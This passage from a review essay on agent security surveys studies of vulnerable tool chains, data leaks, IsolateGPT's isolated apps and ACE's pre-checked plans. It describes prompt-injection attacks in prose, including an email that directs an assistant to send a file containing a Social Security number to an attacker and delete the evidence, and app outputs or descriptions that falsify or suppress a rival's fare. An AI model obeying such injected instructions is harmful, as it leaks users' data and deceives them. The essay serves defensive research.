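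In 225 of the 365 vulnerabilities, the attacker is the user. These matter to a company that hosts an agent for the public, because users' commands run on the company's machines. Someone who runs an agent on their own laptop gains nothing by attacking it. The other 140 vulnerabilities start from outside content. Only 63 of the 365 involve a single tool, so at least 77 of these 140 involve several.

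The total also depends on how one counts vulnerabilities. ChainFuzzer found only 199 tools that contain a sink, so some must account for several vulnerabilities each, and one fix to such a tool could close all of its vulnerabilities. Wu and colleagues suggest restricting what a sink accepts, for example by replacing free-form commands with a fixed template. They also recommend simple flow tracking for data from users or outside sources.

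Ordinary requests would trigger these chains less often than ChainFuzzer does. ChainFuzzer's first draft of each request listed the steps, but the agent completed the chain in only 27% of runs, compared with 95% after revision. The model's safeguards also helped against undisguised attacks. In tests on 100 of the confirmed vulnerabilities, the original harmful input worked in 18% of attempts and the disguised versions in 89%.

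In *Agent Smith in Action*, Zha, Li and colleagues (2026) ran a much larger search, looking for chains among the tools within each of 10,121 MCP servers. They then tested by hand every weakness reported in a random sample of 100 servers. Of the 20 chains reported in the sample, 19 worked. They could not produce the same effect with the last tool alone in any of the 19, so testing tools individually would have missed these chains.

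One of their examples is a server with a tool that runs commands and a tool that writes files. The first tool rejects dangerous commands, but it doesn't check the contents of the scripts it runs. An attacker can have the second tool write a forbidden command into a script file and then have the first tool run it, so the file carries the command from one call to the other. AgentBound runs each server in a single container, so it would not separate these two tools, but it would limit which files the script could damage.

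Chains made up 19 of the 124 weaknesses that Zha and colleagues confirmed, a much smaller share than ChainFuzzer found. This may be because ChainFuzzer examined whole applications, which can combine tools from many sources.

### Leaks without an attacker

*AgentRaft* (Lin, Wu and colleagues, 2026) provides evidence closer to the salary report, which has no attacker. The paper looks for agents that send a third party data that the user didn't ask to share and the task doesn't need. In one case, a user asked an agent called Pokee to email an auditor the date and amount of a payment. The file tool returned the full transaction record, and the agent's email also included the card number and security code.

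Lin and colleagues wrote requests that lead an agent to use a tool that reads private data and then one that sends data out. They tested five existing agents, including Codex, Claude Code and OpenClaw, and found that the agents sent data they should have left out in 759 of 2,337 tests, or 32%. In those 759 tests, about 80% of the data fields sent were unnecessary.

A panel of language models judged which fields were necessary. In a separate test on four agents the researchers had built, people confirmed 295 of the 319 leaking chains the program reported, so its judgments seem fairly reliable. But the 32% is not a rate for everyday use, because the researchers designed the tests to expose this mistake, with files that mixed data to send and data to withhold. All five agents also ran on the same language model, so the result may not hold for the models these products normally use.

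These leaks use the copying path, as in the salary report. Sandboxing the tools would not have helped, because the task required both the file access and the email.

### Four agents compared with operating systems

An operating system keeps programs apart even when they work on the same task. Programs that run one after the other can't read each other's memory, and they exchange data only through explicit channels such as files and pipes. Pirch and colleagues checked whether agents separate their tools similarly. They picked the most popular open-source agent in each of four groups: OpenClaw, a general assistant with many features; IronClaw, a version designed for security; Nanobot, which has a deliberately small code base; and NemoClaw, which runs OpenClaw inside a sandbox.

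None of the four agents deliberately separates the results of successive tools in the model's context, even for IronClaw's sandboxed tools. This finding comes from examining how the agents work rather than from an attack. Old results sometimes disappear when an agent summarises a long conversation, but that is a side effect of saving space.

The researchers then tried 16 attacks on each agent, mostly with default settings. They ran every agent in its own virtual machine, restored the machine to a clean state before each test, and monitored file and network activity from the kernel. An attack counted as successful if it worked at least once in three attempts.

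One attack tested whether data could pass between skills, which are packages of instructions that may include their own programs. One skill saved a secret to a file, and a second skill read it. This worked on OpenClaw, Nanobot and NemoClaw, but the test did not apply to IronClaw. In another attack, a skill's script overwrote the agent's long-term memory, with the same results. Both attacks would have failed if each skill had run in its own sandbox, with its own folder and no write access to the memory files. NemoClaw's sandbox didn't stop them because it surrounds the whole agent.

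Five other attacks targeted either the agent's own code and settings or secrets stored on the machine. All five succeeded against OpenClaw, which has no sandbox by default. One succeeded against IronClaw and one against NemoClaw. Nanobot, with its optional sandbox switched on, resisted all five, but the sandbox still let one skill read another's secret.

All four agents also gave one user's secret to another user who asked for it. The secret leaked through data that each agent stores for several users. Sandboxing each tool would help only if it also kept the users' data separate, because the same tool may serve all of them.

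These results come from Qwen3.5, an open-weight model. Far fewer attacks succeeded on OpenClaw with the newer GPT-5.5, only five of 16, although Pirch and colleagues did not adapt the prompts to get around its refusals. One of the five was the leak between skills, which worked on OpenClaw with all four models they tried. They conclude that isolating the tools' execution is not enough on its own.

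### Weaknesses and actual attacks

These studies show that paths for attacks exist in widely used software, but none measured how often attacks happen. Li and colleagues installed the malicious helpers themselves. Wu and colleagues chose popular applications and revised their requests until the chains worked, and Pirch and colleagues supplied the malicious skills.

Zha and colleagues come closest to measuring a rate, because they sampled 100 servers at random. They confirmed chains on nine of them. The true number is probably higher, since a version of their program with fewer filters found eight more working chains in the same sample, along with many false alarms. But the servers date from mid-2025, and they did not weight the sample by how much people use each server. For the full collection, the program produced 27,123 reports, 31% of them chains. Zha and colleagues warn that this is not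 the share of real vulnerabilities, because they did not test most of the reports.

Public records contain far fewer cases. *Tracing MCP Security Vulnerabilities* (2026) reviewed 119 entries in CVE, the standard public list of software flaws, and found 24 genuine MCP vulnerabilities as of February 2026. Most of them let an attacker run commands or reach files outside a permitted folder. These are also weaknesses rather than attacks. A list of flaws in individual products could easily miss harm caused by combining several products.

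In February 2026, the malware-scanning service VirusTotal documented hundreds of malicious third-party skills for OpenClaw, according to Pirch and colleagues. An attack like the one in *Les Dissonances* therefore has a realistic starting point. However, this count doesn't show how many people installed the skills, or whether the skills interfered with other tools rather than attacking the user's machine directly.

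## IsolateGPT: a separate model and memory for each app

Sandboxes around the tools don't divide the model's context, and most of the attacks on real agents went through that context. IsolateGPT divides it by giving each app a separate model and memory, with a trusted hub that passes messages between the apps. An app here is a set of related functions with a description for the model, such as a mail app that can search, draft and send. Wu, Roesner and colleagues first described the design in *SECGPT* (2024) and renamed it IsolateGPT for the NDSS security conference in 2025.

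### The comparison with web browsers

Wu and colleagues base their argument on the history of web browsers. Browsers first separated websites with the same-origin policy, a rule that normally stops one site from reading another's data. But pages from several sites could run in one process, so the rule depended on the browser's code having no serious bugs. *Site Isolation*, a page by Chromium, the open-source project behind Chrome, counts 5 to 15 potentially exploitable bugs in the code that displays pages in each of five successive releases. Spectre, an attack that exploits how processors run instructions before knowing whether they are needed, could read a process's memory even without a browser bug.

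Chrome now puts each site in its own sandboxed process, at least on desktop computers. *Site Isolation* (Reis, Moshchuk and Oskov, 2019) describes how a more privileged browser process coordinates the rest. If a page contains a frame from another site, the page and the frame can still exchange messages, but the browser process relays them. The browser process also keeps most of one site's data out of another site's process.

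In an ordinary agent, a hostile app description can change how the model uses every other app, much as an attacker who takes over a shared browser process can reach every site in it. IsolateGPT is laid out like a browser that gives each site its own process. It runs each app with its own model in a separate process, called a spoke, and a hub takes the place of the browser's main process.

The comparison is imperfect, as Wu and colleagues acknowledge. Apps in an agent work together all the time and need a lot of information about the user, so an app in a closed sandbox would be nearly useless. They also communicate in ordinary language. A browser only has to deliver a message to the right site, whose code then interprets it. In an agent, a message delivered to the right app can still be unsafe, because the language model that reads it may follow instructions in it.

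### The hub and the spokes

The hub's operator is an ordinary program with a fixed sequence of steps and no language model, so a cleverly worded message can't change what it does. For decisions that require understanding the request, the operator calls the hub's planner, which is a language model. The planner reads the user's request, the earlier conversation and the descriptions of the available apps. It chooses the apps for the task and works out whether one will need data from another. The hub's memory holds the user's conversations with all the apps, summaries of those conversations, and facts about the user such as a date of birth.

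Each spoke has its own operator, model and memory. The spoke's model sees the user's request, any data the hub has passed on, and past conversations with that one app. It also sees a general list of functions the system supports, such as web browsing or meeting scheduling. The list doesn't show which apps the user has installed, because a malicious app could use that information to recognise the user.

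Each spoke also runs in an operating-system sandbox. A seccomp filter limits its system calls, and the app can contact only its own internet domain.

For a request that needs one app, the operator uses the planner to choose a suitable app and retrieves from the hub's memory the data that app seems to need. If the user agrees to share the data, the operator starts the spoke. The spoke's model then makes its own plan and carries it out, but the user must confirm any irreversible action, such as sending an email or making a purchase.

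### How two apps exchange messages

Spokes can't contact each other directly. If a mail app needs a file from a cloud drive, the exchange goes like this:

1. The mail spoke's model decides that it needs a function its own app lacks. Its operator requests the function from the hub, without naming an app.
2. The hub's operator finds an app with that function. It replies with the format for the request and the response, and with a temporary identifier in place of the app's name.
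3. The mail spoke's model writes a request in that format, and its operator sends it to the hub.
4. The hub shows the user a permission dialog and relays the request if the user agrees.
5. The drive spoke's operator checks the format. Its model then uses the drive app to produce a response, and its operator checks that too and sends it to the hub.
6. The hub relays the response, again with the user's consent. The mail spoke's operator checks the format before its model reads anything.

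The function request in step 1 needs consent as well, so one exchange could produce three dialogs.

The developer of each app declares what type of data every function accepts and returns, and the operators drop messages that don't fit. This works well against injected instructions when the type is narrow, since a date can't contain a command to email a stranger. It does much less to prevent leaks, because a salary is a valid number. Many functions also need free text, which can contain anything. Wu and colleagues know of no foolproof way to detect malicious instructions in text automatically, so they have the user read these messages.

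To help the user decide, the hub compares each request with the plan it made at the start. If the plan didn't have these two apps working together, the dialog includes a warning. Wu and colleagues consider this assessment hard to manipulate, because the planner works only from the user's request, app descriptions and stored data, and they assume someone has vetted the descriptions and data. The ACE paper later presented an attack on the hub through this planning step.

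Users can also see fewer dialogs by allowing two apps to communicate for a whole session or permanently. A permanent permission covers everything the two apps send each other, so the user no longer sees each message. It can't cover irreversible actions, which the app's developer or a reviewer has to mark as irreversible.

### A malicious email and a cloud drive

Wu and colleagues tested the design against an attack that uses LangChain's apps for Gmail and Google Drive. In the short version from their conference slides, a user asks for a summary of the latest email. The email tells the user's assistant to find a file containing a Social Security number, email a link to it to the attacker, and delete both messages.

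The IsolateGPT paper compares IsolateGPT with its own VanillaGPT, a system with the same features but a single context for all apps. VanillaGPT's model read the email, fetched the document, sent it and deleted the evidence.

In IsolateGPT, the hub's plan for this request has one step, a search of the inbox. The mail spoke's model then reads the email and may well follow the instructions in it, which isolation doesn't prevent. But this model has no drive functions, so its operator has to request the file through the hub. Because the plan doesn't include the drive, the user sees a warning. In the test the user refused, so the attacker got nothing. If the user had given the two apps permanent permission beforehand, the only remaining check would have been the confirmation before the email went out.

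The attack would be harder to spot if the user's own request involved both apps. Suppose the user asks the agent to reply to an email with the file the sender requested. That task requires the mail app to contact the drive. The hub compares only which apps work together, so it would probably give no warning even if the sender had requested the wrong file. The user would have to catch the attack by noticing the file's name.

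The result of a test with two ride-sharing apps depended less on the user. One app, Quick Ride, included an instruction to add $10 to every fare from its rival, Metro Hail, and VanillaGPT's model followed it. In IsolateGPT, each app reported its fare from its own spoke, and a third spoke with no app compared them, so Quick Ride's instruction had no effect.

In another test, a user gave a medical booking app personal details, including recent heart surgery, and later booked a flight. VanillaGPT passed the medical details to the travel app. IsolateGPT asked for permission to share the stored data, and the user refused. The travel app then didn't have the user's name or email address, so the user had to type them in. Wu and colleagues accept this extra effort in exchange for the protection.

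### The test with 1,598 attacks

Wu and colleagues ran a larger test with the 1,054 cases in InjecAgent, using the stronger form that begins with an order to ignore previous instructions. They added 544 attacks on data in the system's own memory. Both systems ran on a 2023 version of GPT-4. The table combines the detailed results with the totals on the slides.

| Goal of the attack | Attacks | Succeeded without isolation | Permission dialog with isolation |
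|---|---|---|---|
| Misuse another app | 510 | 23.2% | 5.6% |
| Steal another app's data | 544 | 34.4% | 15.2% |
| Steal data from the system's memory | 544 | 3.2% | 2.0% |
| All | 1,598 | 20.2% | 7.6% |

Every one of the dialogs included a warning.

The 7.6% is the share of cases, about 120 of 1,598, in which the attack got far enough that the outcome depended on what the user clicked. It is not an attack success rate, because no users took part in the test. The slides therefore give ranges, such as 0% to 15.2% for stealing another app's data. The lower end assumes that users refuse every request, and the upper end that they approve every one. Wu and colleagues favour the lower end. In their instructions for reproducing the case studies, they assume that users reject requests with warnings, and they tell the tester to do the same.

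Even if users approved everything, the attacks would succeed less than half as often as against VanillaGPT. One likely reason is that a hijacked model in a spoke doesn't have the other app's functions in its context and has to request them first. The low numbers for the system's memory are weak evidence about either design. Wu and colleagues attribute them mainly to the attack prompts, which name the data differently from how a real system may store it.

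The perfect record on warnings is also partly due to the test's design. Each user request in Zhan and colleagues' InjecAgent needs only one tool, so any contact with a second app falls outside the hub's plan, and the hub can flag it without judging whether it is malicious. The test contained no legitimate requests for a second app, so it couldn't measure how often the hub warns about harmless ones. Users who see many false warnings may start to ignore the real ones. The PFI paper later tested IsolateGPT against its own system on different tasks.

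### How users respond to permission requests

*How Agents Ask for Permission* (Michael and Roesner, 2026) reviews 21 proposals for letting users control what agents may do. Michael and Roesner found that only three, including IsolateGPT, which Roesner also worked on, leave it to the user to spot violations. IsolateGPT does apply lasting permissions reliably, though, because an ordinary program enforces them. Commercial products rely on users more. Four of the five agents that Michael and Roesner tried interrupted users with frequent permission requests at least some of the time.

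Several of IsolateGPT's designers later studied how people make such decisions. In *Towards Automating Data Access Permissions in AI Agents* (Wu, Yang and colleagues, 2025), 205 people decided what data an imaginary assistant could share. Every permission question came with a reminder that the assistant might request too much. Participants shared unneeded data 78.2% of the time when they believed the task required it, and refused 62.5% of the time when they recognised that it didn't. This suggests that people often approve requests for unneeded data because they don't know what the task requires, and a warning based on the hub's plan could help with that.

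In a smaller experiment on actions rather than data, Yan (2026), in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, had 113 people without software backgrounds supervise an assistant through a short simulation of one day. Seven of the assistant's 18 actions went beyond what the user had requested. Participants who had to approve every action still approved those seven in 40.3% of cases. Some were fairly harmless, such as calling the airport to confirm a flight, but 35.3% of participants let the assistant read private messages.

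Another group in Yan's experiment set standing rules for four kinds of action, a little like IsolateGPT's lasting permissions. They saw an average of 10.9 permission requests instead of 18. But they set 114 of their 140 rules to "ask", and when the assistant asked to do something beyond what the user had asked for, they approved it 66.8% of the time. Lasting permissions may therefore reduce the number of requests without improving users' decisions on the ones that remain.

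The worst results come from coding. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes a study in which 1,053 paid testers worked through a session with the coding agent. During the session, one permission request showed a clearly dangerous command in place of a routine one. Only 13.6% of the testers refused it. The refusal rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more requests. Anthropic had an interest in this result because it was arguing for an automated check to replace the requests, but the decline fits the idea that people stop reading them.

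None of these experiments used a warning like IsolateGPT's, which appears when a request departs from a plan. People may well take such a warning more seriously than a plain request, especially if it is rare. Still, given these results, it is hard to assume that users would refuse all of the roughly 120 requests in the attack test.

Wu, Yang and colleagues propose automating the decisions with a program that learns from a user's past choices and those of similar users. It predicted participants' choices correctly 85.1% of the time, or 94.4% when it made only confident predictions. This could remove many dialogs. But because the program predicts what a user would choose, it could also repeat users' oversharing, and the same participants often shared data that the task didn't need.

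### Functionality, time and cost

To check that isolation doesn't break anything, Wu and colleagues ran 103 queries from LangChain's public benchmarks on IsolateGPT and VanillaGPT. Both systems completed every query that needed one app or several independent apps. Where apps had to share data, both gave the right final answer on 20 of 21 queries (95%). On queries without apps, their scores differed by one percentage point.

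Some of these tasks are very artificial. The benchmark with several independent apps has 26 apps that each type one letter, and the agent calls up to 13 of them to spell out a string. The queries that required collaboration are closer to real use, but there are only 21 of them.

| Type of query | Queries | Average time without isolation | Average time with isolation |
|---|---|---|---|
| No app | 42 | 19.5 seconds | 21.4 seconds |
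| One app | 20 | 32.0 seconds | 39.2 seconds |
| Several independent apps | 20 | 30.3 seconds | 65.3 seconds |
| Several apps that share data | 21 | 24.7 seconds | 49.3 seconds |

Wu and colleagues emphasise that IsolateGPT added less than 30% to the time taken for 75.73% of the queries. However, 62 of the 103 queries used one app or none, and isolation matters most when a query uses several. The average time roughly doubled for queries that used several apps, whether or not the apps shared data.

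Almost all of the extra time went into planning and finding data in memory, mostly in the spokes. Every spoke started from scratch in these tests, so a system that kept its spokes running would be faster. But the tests granted every permission automatically, and a real user would need time to read the dialogs.

IsolateGPT also cost 1.85 times as much to run, based on a calculation from a tenth of the queries. Wu and colleagues note that a newer version of GPT-4 was already about 12 times cheaper than the one they used. Cheaper models lower the cost, but an isolated agent would still make more model calls than an ordinary one.

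Years of engineering have reduced the overhead of browser isolation. Gazelle, an early research browser, took about 44% longer to load a website, while Reis and colleagues report that isolation in Chrome added less than 2.25% to loading time and 9% to 13% to memory use. IsolateGPT could achieve similar reductions, for example by planning for several apps at once. But its main overhead is extra work by language models, which is harder to reduce than the overhead of running more processes.

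### Attacks inside one app, and free text between apps

Wu and colleagues exclude attacks that stay within a single app. IsolateGPT is designed to stop a malicious email from reaching the cloud drive, but not to protect the mail app from the email. A hijacked mail spoke could still give the user a false summary of the inbox or draft a message that quotes other emails, although the user would have to confirm the message before it was sent. Chrome's isolation has a similar limit, since it separates sites from each other but doesn't stop an attacker who inserts hostile code into a site's own pages.

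How much this exclusion matters depends on what counts as one app. If a company offered mail and file storage as a single office app, both would share a spoke. An attack through the malicious email could then reach the file without any message passing through the hub, and the user would see no warning about the drive.

The design relies on the user to screen each free-text message between apps. For the salary report, the user asks for a summary by email, so the hub's plan would include the spreadsheet, the web and the mail app. The mail spoke would request the salary data and the benchmarks through the hub. Both requests match the plan, so neither dialog would contain a warning. The spoke's model would then write the summary, and the user would confirm the email.

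A careful user could stop the leak at either point, an opportunity that a sandbox around each tool doesn't provide. But IsolateGPT doesn't label the salary data, so the confirmation would not show that a sentence about engineers' pay came from an internal spreadsheet. The user would have to recognise the source themselves, and may be inclined to approve the email because they asked for it.

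## ACE: attacks through IsolateGPT's hub, and a plan checked before it runs

IsolateGPT depends on its hub to stop one app's instructions from affecting another app. *ACE* (Li, Mallick and colleagues, 2025) identifies three ways for a malicious app to get past the hub, and presents a system of the same name, short for Abstract-Concrete-Execute. The system writes the whole plan before any app's text can influence it, and checks where the data would go before running anything.

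### Three attacks with two ride-sharing apps

The attacks reuse the two apps from IsolateGPT's own tests, the honest Metro Hail and the malicious Quick Ride. A user asks what a trip would cost with each. Li, Mallick and colleagues (2026) specify in the final version of *ACE*, published at the NDSS conference, that they ran all three attacks on IsolateGPT's public code.

One attack uses an app's output to stop the remaining steps. The system first calls Quick Ride, which returns a warning instead of a fare, claiming that all fare calculators are part of a drug distribution scheme. The model handling the request then stops before it calls Metro Hail. The user gets no fare, only a vague message about a technical error that doesn't identify which app caused the problem.

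Another attack changes a competitor's result. Metro Hail runs first and returns a fare of $54. Quick Ride then returns an instruction to report $54 for Quick Ride and $85 for Metro Hail. The model in Quick Ride's spoke repeats the instruction word for word, and the model that writes the final answer follows it.

The last attack works through an app's description, before any app has run. Quick Ride's description includes an instruction to use Quick Ride whenever the user wants a fare from Metro Hail. The planner then omits Metro Hail, so the user gets only one fare even though the request named both apps.

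In their conference slides, Mallick, Rose and colleagues (2026) give a more destructive example, in which a user asks an agent to email a file and the description of an unrelated calculator app contains an instruction to delete everything on the disk. They use it to illustrate the danger for agents that plan one step at a time, and don't report testing it. Li and colleagues show one run of each attack on IsolateGPT, so the attacks are clearly possible, but they give no success rates, so we can't tell how reliable the attacks are.

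### Two descriptions of the hub

The fare-changing attack looks much like the one that failed in Wu and colleagues' test. The likely difference is which model the instruction reached. In the earlier test, it reached only the model in Quick Ride's spoke, and a separate spoke with no app compared the fares. In the newer attack, the instruction is the result that Quick Ride's spoke returns, so the spoke only has to pass it on to a model that has both fares in its context.

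The two papers describe that model differently. Wu and colleagues emphasise that the hub's operator contains no language model, and they leave the comparison to the empty spoke. Li and colleagues describe an "execution manager" inside the hub that has its own language model. It takes the list of apps from the planner, chooses which one to call next, reads the raw output and decides what to do after that. Wu and colleagues don't name such a component, but their empty spoke does a similar job when it requests a result from each app and combines them. The papers may well describe the same model but draw the hub's boundary in different places.

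The boundary does little to stop the attack, because some model has to read both fares to compare them, and any text that arrives in place of a fare can influence that model.

IsolateGPT's format checks should block the hostile sentence if Quick Ride may return only a number. Wu and colleagues assume that someone reviews these formats before an app reaches the store. Li and colleagues let the attacker write the format too, so Quick Ride could declare that it returns text. The user might still notice the odd message in a permission dialog, but the dialog would probably carry no warning because the request involves both apps.

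Wu and colleagues also did not set out to prevent the attack through the description, because they assume that descriptions are vetted. Li and colleagues accept this and rate IsolateGPT's planning as secure when the descriptions are honest. They make a similar criticism of f-Secure, an earlier design that plans only from trusted input but counts app descriptions as trusted. The two attacks through outputs are more serious for IsolateGPT because they work even with an honest description, at least if the app may return free text, and because Wu and colleagues did intend to stop a compromised app from affecting others.

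### A plan made from the request alone

ACE's planner receives the user's request, but no text from any app and no information about which apps the user has installed. An operator can add a short, trusted description of the setting, such as what kind of database the agent works with, but it must not contain anything supplied by an app.

A language model first invents apps suited to the task, which Li and colleagues call abstract apps. Each has a name, a description, and types for its inputs and output, but no code. For a request to summarise a file, the model might invent one app that loads documents and another that summarises text. In a second call, the model writes a short program that uses these apps. The program loads the file, passes the text to the summariser and displays the result.

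This program, the abstract plan, is written in a cut-down version of Python. It can branch and loop, but it can't open files itself or run code that it generates while running. Every variable has a declared type, and Li and colleagues ban lists and other data structures that can be changed in place. These restrictions make it easier for a separate program to work out where the data will go.

Plans can still be fairly elaborate. In one test, a user asked whether Bob and Alice live in the same city. Before seeing any of the data, the model wrote a plan that looks up each person's ID, then the ID of their location, then the city, with a branch in case the database has nobody by that name. The plan then uses ordinary code to compare the two cities.

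### Matching the plan to installed apps

ACE then looks for an installed app to match each abstract one. It discards installed apps whose descriptions differ too much from the abstract app's. For each remaining pair, a language model decides whether the installed app can do the abstract app's job. If so, the model also writes small functions that convert inputs and outputs between the two apps' formats.

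The model judges every pair separately, so Quick Ride's description is not in its context when it considers Metro Hail. Quick Ride can no longer remove its competitor, though it can still exaggerate what it does itself. The model also writes the conversion functions just after reading the app's description, so an attacker could try to influence that code through the description. Li and colleagues' attack doesn't test this, because it used a description only to exclude a rival.

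When several apps fit the same step, ACE prefers the combination that needs the fewest privileges, but only where the comparison is clear. For example, it prefers a combination that needs only file access to one that needs both file and network access. If one needs only file access and another needs only network access, ACE picks at random. Developers declare the privileges of their own apps, so a malicious developer could request very few to get an app chosen, but the app would then be limited to those privileges.

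### The bank-details plan

Before running a plan, ACE checks the plan's data flows with a lattice of labels like Denning's. In Li and colleagues' example, a label is a set of categories such as financial and personal. Each app has a clearance, which is also a set of categories. The symbols ⊑ and ⊔ correspond to Denning's → and ⊕. Here x ⊑ y holds if every category in x is also in y, and x ⊔ y is the set of all categories in x or y.

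If an app with clearance f receives inputs with labels x₁ to xₙ, the plan has to satisfy

x₁ ⊔ x₂ ⊔ … ⊔ xₙ ⊑ f

and the app's output then gets the label f. Li and colleagues show how this works with a plan of two lines:

```
data = load_bank_details()
send_email(content=data)
```

The banking app has the clearance {financial} and the mail app has {personal}. Suppose that the user has labelled the request as containing nothing sensitive. The check then goes through the plan as follows:

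1. The banking app receives no sensitive data, so the call is allowed. Its result, which the plan stores in the variable `data`, gets the label {financial}.
2. The mail app would receive `data`. That requires {financial} ⊑ {personal}, which is false, because "financial" is not in the mail app's clearance.
3. ACE rejects this combination of apps and tries any others that fit. If none of them passes, it stops with an error.

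No app has run at this point, so the bank details have not been sent anywhere. A mail app with the clearance {financial, personal} would pass the same check.

The check also catches less obvious leaks. In one example, a loop sends the contents of a variable over the network and then loads bank details into that variable. The bank details leak only from the second pass onward, so ACE repeats its analysis of the loop until the labels stop changing. In another example, a plan writes "0" or "1" depending on the first character of a secret. This is one of Denning's implicit flows, and the check gives the result the secret's label.

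ACE checks a plan before running it, whereas CaMeL's interpreter applies its restrictions while the program runs. ACE can therefore refuse a task before any app receives data. Li and colleagues do not prove that the check catches every leak. They chose Python because language models write it well, but its complicated behaviour makes a proof difficult. They suggest a purpose-built language as future work.

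### Running the plan in containers

ACE runs the plan in one Docker container and each app in its own. The plan's container has no file access and can communicate only with the orchestrator, a trusted program that manages the containers. When the plan reaches a call, the orchestrator passes the arguments to the app's container, checks that the result has the right type and returns it to the plan. It also shuts down apps that run for too long.

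All three attacks failed when Li and colleagues repeated them on ACE. In the attacks through outputs, the plan called both apps and expected a number from each. Quick Ride's hostile text caused a type error, which the user saw next to Metro Hail's correct fare. If the plan had accepted text, the hostile sentence would have appeared under Quick Ride's name, but no model would have acted on it. Quick Ride could still return a false fare for its own ride, since a false number would pass the type check.

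Li and colleagues say in the 2025 version that an app's output never enters a model's prompt. This is true of ACE's own planning models, but an app may contain a language model too. A summarising app almost certainly does, and a hostile web page could cause it to write a misleading summary. The page couldn't add a step to the plan, and it couldn't change who receives the summary if the address came from the user's request rather than from an app.

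### Security and task success

Li and colleagues tested ACE on the 1,054 cases in InjecAgent, changing the benchmark so that ACE handled each request from the beginning. ACE never called an attacker's app, whichever models it used. The design should guarantee this, because ACE fixes the plan before the hostile text arrives, so the test mostly confirms that the program works as intended.

The share of user tasks that ACE completed is more informative, and it changed a lot between the two versions of the paper.

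| Models | Task success, 2025 version | Task success, 2026 version |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o for planning, o3-mini for matching | 75.2% | 85.3% |
| GPT-4o for both | 47.2% | 83.6% |
| Claude 3.7 Sonnet for both | 66.7% | 60.7% |
| Qwen 2.5 72B for both | 67.8% | 60.2% |

The models have the same names in both versions, so most of the change probably comes from ACE itself or from how Li and colleagues ran the test. For example, only the later version describes the trusted note about the setting, which helps the planner guess what kinds of apps exist. The large change in GPT-4o's results suggests that such details can matter more than the choice of model.

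Even the 85.3% success rate may overstate how well ACE works. The benchmark counts a success when ACE chooses the right app and runs it without an error, but doesn't check whether the answer is correct. The apps are also simple simulations.

A second benchmark, Agent Security Bench, covers ten kinds of agent. On it, ACE called an attacker's app in three of 2,000 trials and completed at least 86% of the tasks with GPT-4o or GPT-4.1. In those three trials, the app's description happened to suit the task. For instance, ACE chose an attacker's market analysis app for a question about investing in a new sector. Li and colleagues don't count these calls as violations, because the injected instructions played no part. But a malicious app could still get into a plan just by offering a relevant service, and ACE would then give it whatever data the plan and the app's clearance allow.

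The best comparison with IsolateGPT comes from three sets of LangChain tasks that both systems attempted.

| Tasks | IsolateGPT | ACE with GPT-4o | ACE with GPT-4.1 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Typing a word with one app | 100% | 100% | 95% |
| Typing a word with 26 one-letter apps | 100% | 80% | 80% |
| Answering questions from a database | 95% | 81% | 85.7% |

ACE did worse than IsolateGPT on most of these tasks despite using newer models, which suggests that its stricter planning reduces performance. Each set contains only about 20 queries, so the size of the gap is uncertain. The model pair that did best on InjecAgent scored only 66.7% on the database questions.

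ACE was faster than IsolateGPT, but the difference may have little to do with their designs. With GPT-4.1, ACE took an average of 21 seconds on the tasks with 26 apps. Li and colleagues compare this with 127 seconds for IsolateGPT, but that figure comes from the two queries that needed the most apps. IsolateGPT's average for the whole set was 65 seconds, and it ran on an older model. ACE's cost also grows with the number of installed apps, because it may need a model call for every pair of abstract and real apps. With GPT-4.1, a query cost about $0.01 with one app and $0.27 with 26.

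### What the planner cannot see

Many of ACE's failures occur because its planner can't see the descriptions of installed apps, a restriction that also protects ACE from attacks. In one InjecAgent case, a user asks the agent to find "my future flight". The planner invents an app that searches for flights by origin, destination and date. The user wants to look up an existing reservation, which the installed Expedia app can do. The matching model treats these as different functions, so ACE can't carry out the request. An ordinary agent would have seen the Expedia app's description and could have worked out that the user had already booked. Li and colleagues suggest that users add more detail to their requests, which would help here but requires users to anticipate the misunderstanding.

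Other failures occur after ACE has picked the right app. For example, a user asks for details about a file in Dropbox, but the conversion function looks for the file's size in the wrong part of the result, and the program crashes. An ordinary agent could read the result and answer anyway. ACE doesn't show results to its planner, because reading them to fix mistakes would also expose the planner to any instructions an attacker had put there.

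The restriction also rules out tasks whose steps depend on what the agent finds, unless the planner foresaw the possibilities. A plan can include steps for a name missing from the database, for example. But if a user asks the agent to deal with whatever requests are in the inbox, the planner can't write steps for emails it hasn't read. ACE could pass the emails to an app with its own language model, but that app could act only through the calls already in the plan.

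### The salary report under ACE

ACE can stop the leak in the salary report without relying on the user to notice it. Suppose the spreadsheet app and the summariser have Internal clearance, and the web and mail apps have Public clearance. The plan would pass an Internal summary to a Public mail app, so ACE would reject it before opening the spreadsheet. Rewording the figures in the summary wouldn't change this, because the summary's label depends only on the plan.

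However, clearances belong to apps rather than to recipients, so the same rule would also block an email to the finance director. If the company raised the mail app's clearance to Internal, the check would allow the summary to go to anyone. The company would need two mail apps, one of them restricted to internal addresses.

ACE would also restrict the harmless version of the task. In Denning's model, a summary of public benchmarks stays Public, but in ACE an app's output takes the app's full clearance, because the app might add other data it can access. The summariser needs an Internal clearance to read salaries, so everything it writes counts as Internal, including a summary of a public web page. This label creep comes from the app rather than the data. ACE would refuse to email the summary of the public page unless the user had also installed a summariser with a Public clearance.

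ACE also relies on the user to label every source of information, including the request itself, and the check will miss a leak if a label is wrong or missing. Users have to judge the sensitivity of their data before a task, instead of judging messages during it as they do with IsolateGPT. That probably means fewer interruptions, but a single mistake could affect many tasks. Li and colleagues point to research on inferring privacy settings automatically, which ACE doesn't yet use.

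The labels control which apps receive data, but not what a cleared app does with it. If a malicious summariser has an Internal clearance and its container allows network access, it could send the salaries to its developer. ACE would have approved the plan, and the leak would happen inside a single permitted call.

ACE also handles each request separately, so a user can't follow up with "now send that to Bob". It supports only standalone apps, not suites of related apps such as an office package. Li and colleagues leave both limitations for future work.

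They also exclude attacks on the containers themselves. An app could avoid the flow check by breaking out of its container, or by getting information about other programs through a side channel, an indirect signal such as how long an operation takes. The plan's own container is another risk. If faulty or hostile code took it over, that code could request app calls that the plan never made. The orchestrator couldn't distinguish these from real calls, because it can't observe how far the plan has progressed.

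## PFI: separating trusted from untrusted data, tested against IsolateGPT

ACE writes its whole plan before it has any data, so it struggles with tasks whose later steps depend on what the agent finds. Two other designs, f-secure (2024) and PFI, plan one step at a time, as an ordinary agent does, and hide only the untrusted results from the planning model. PFI also lets the user decide when untrusted data may influence the plan. The PFI paper compares the design directly with f-secure and IsolateGPT.

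### Hidden results in f-secure

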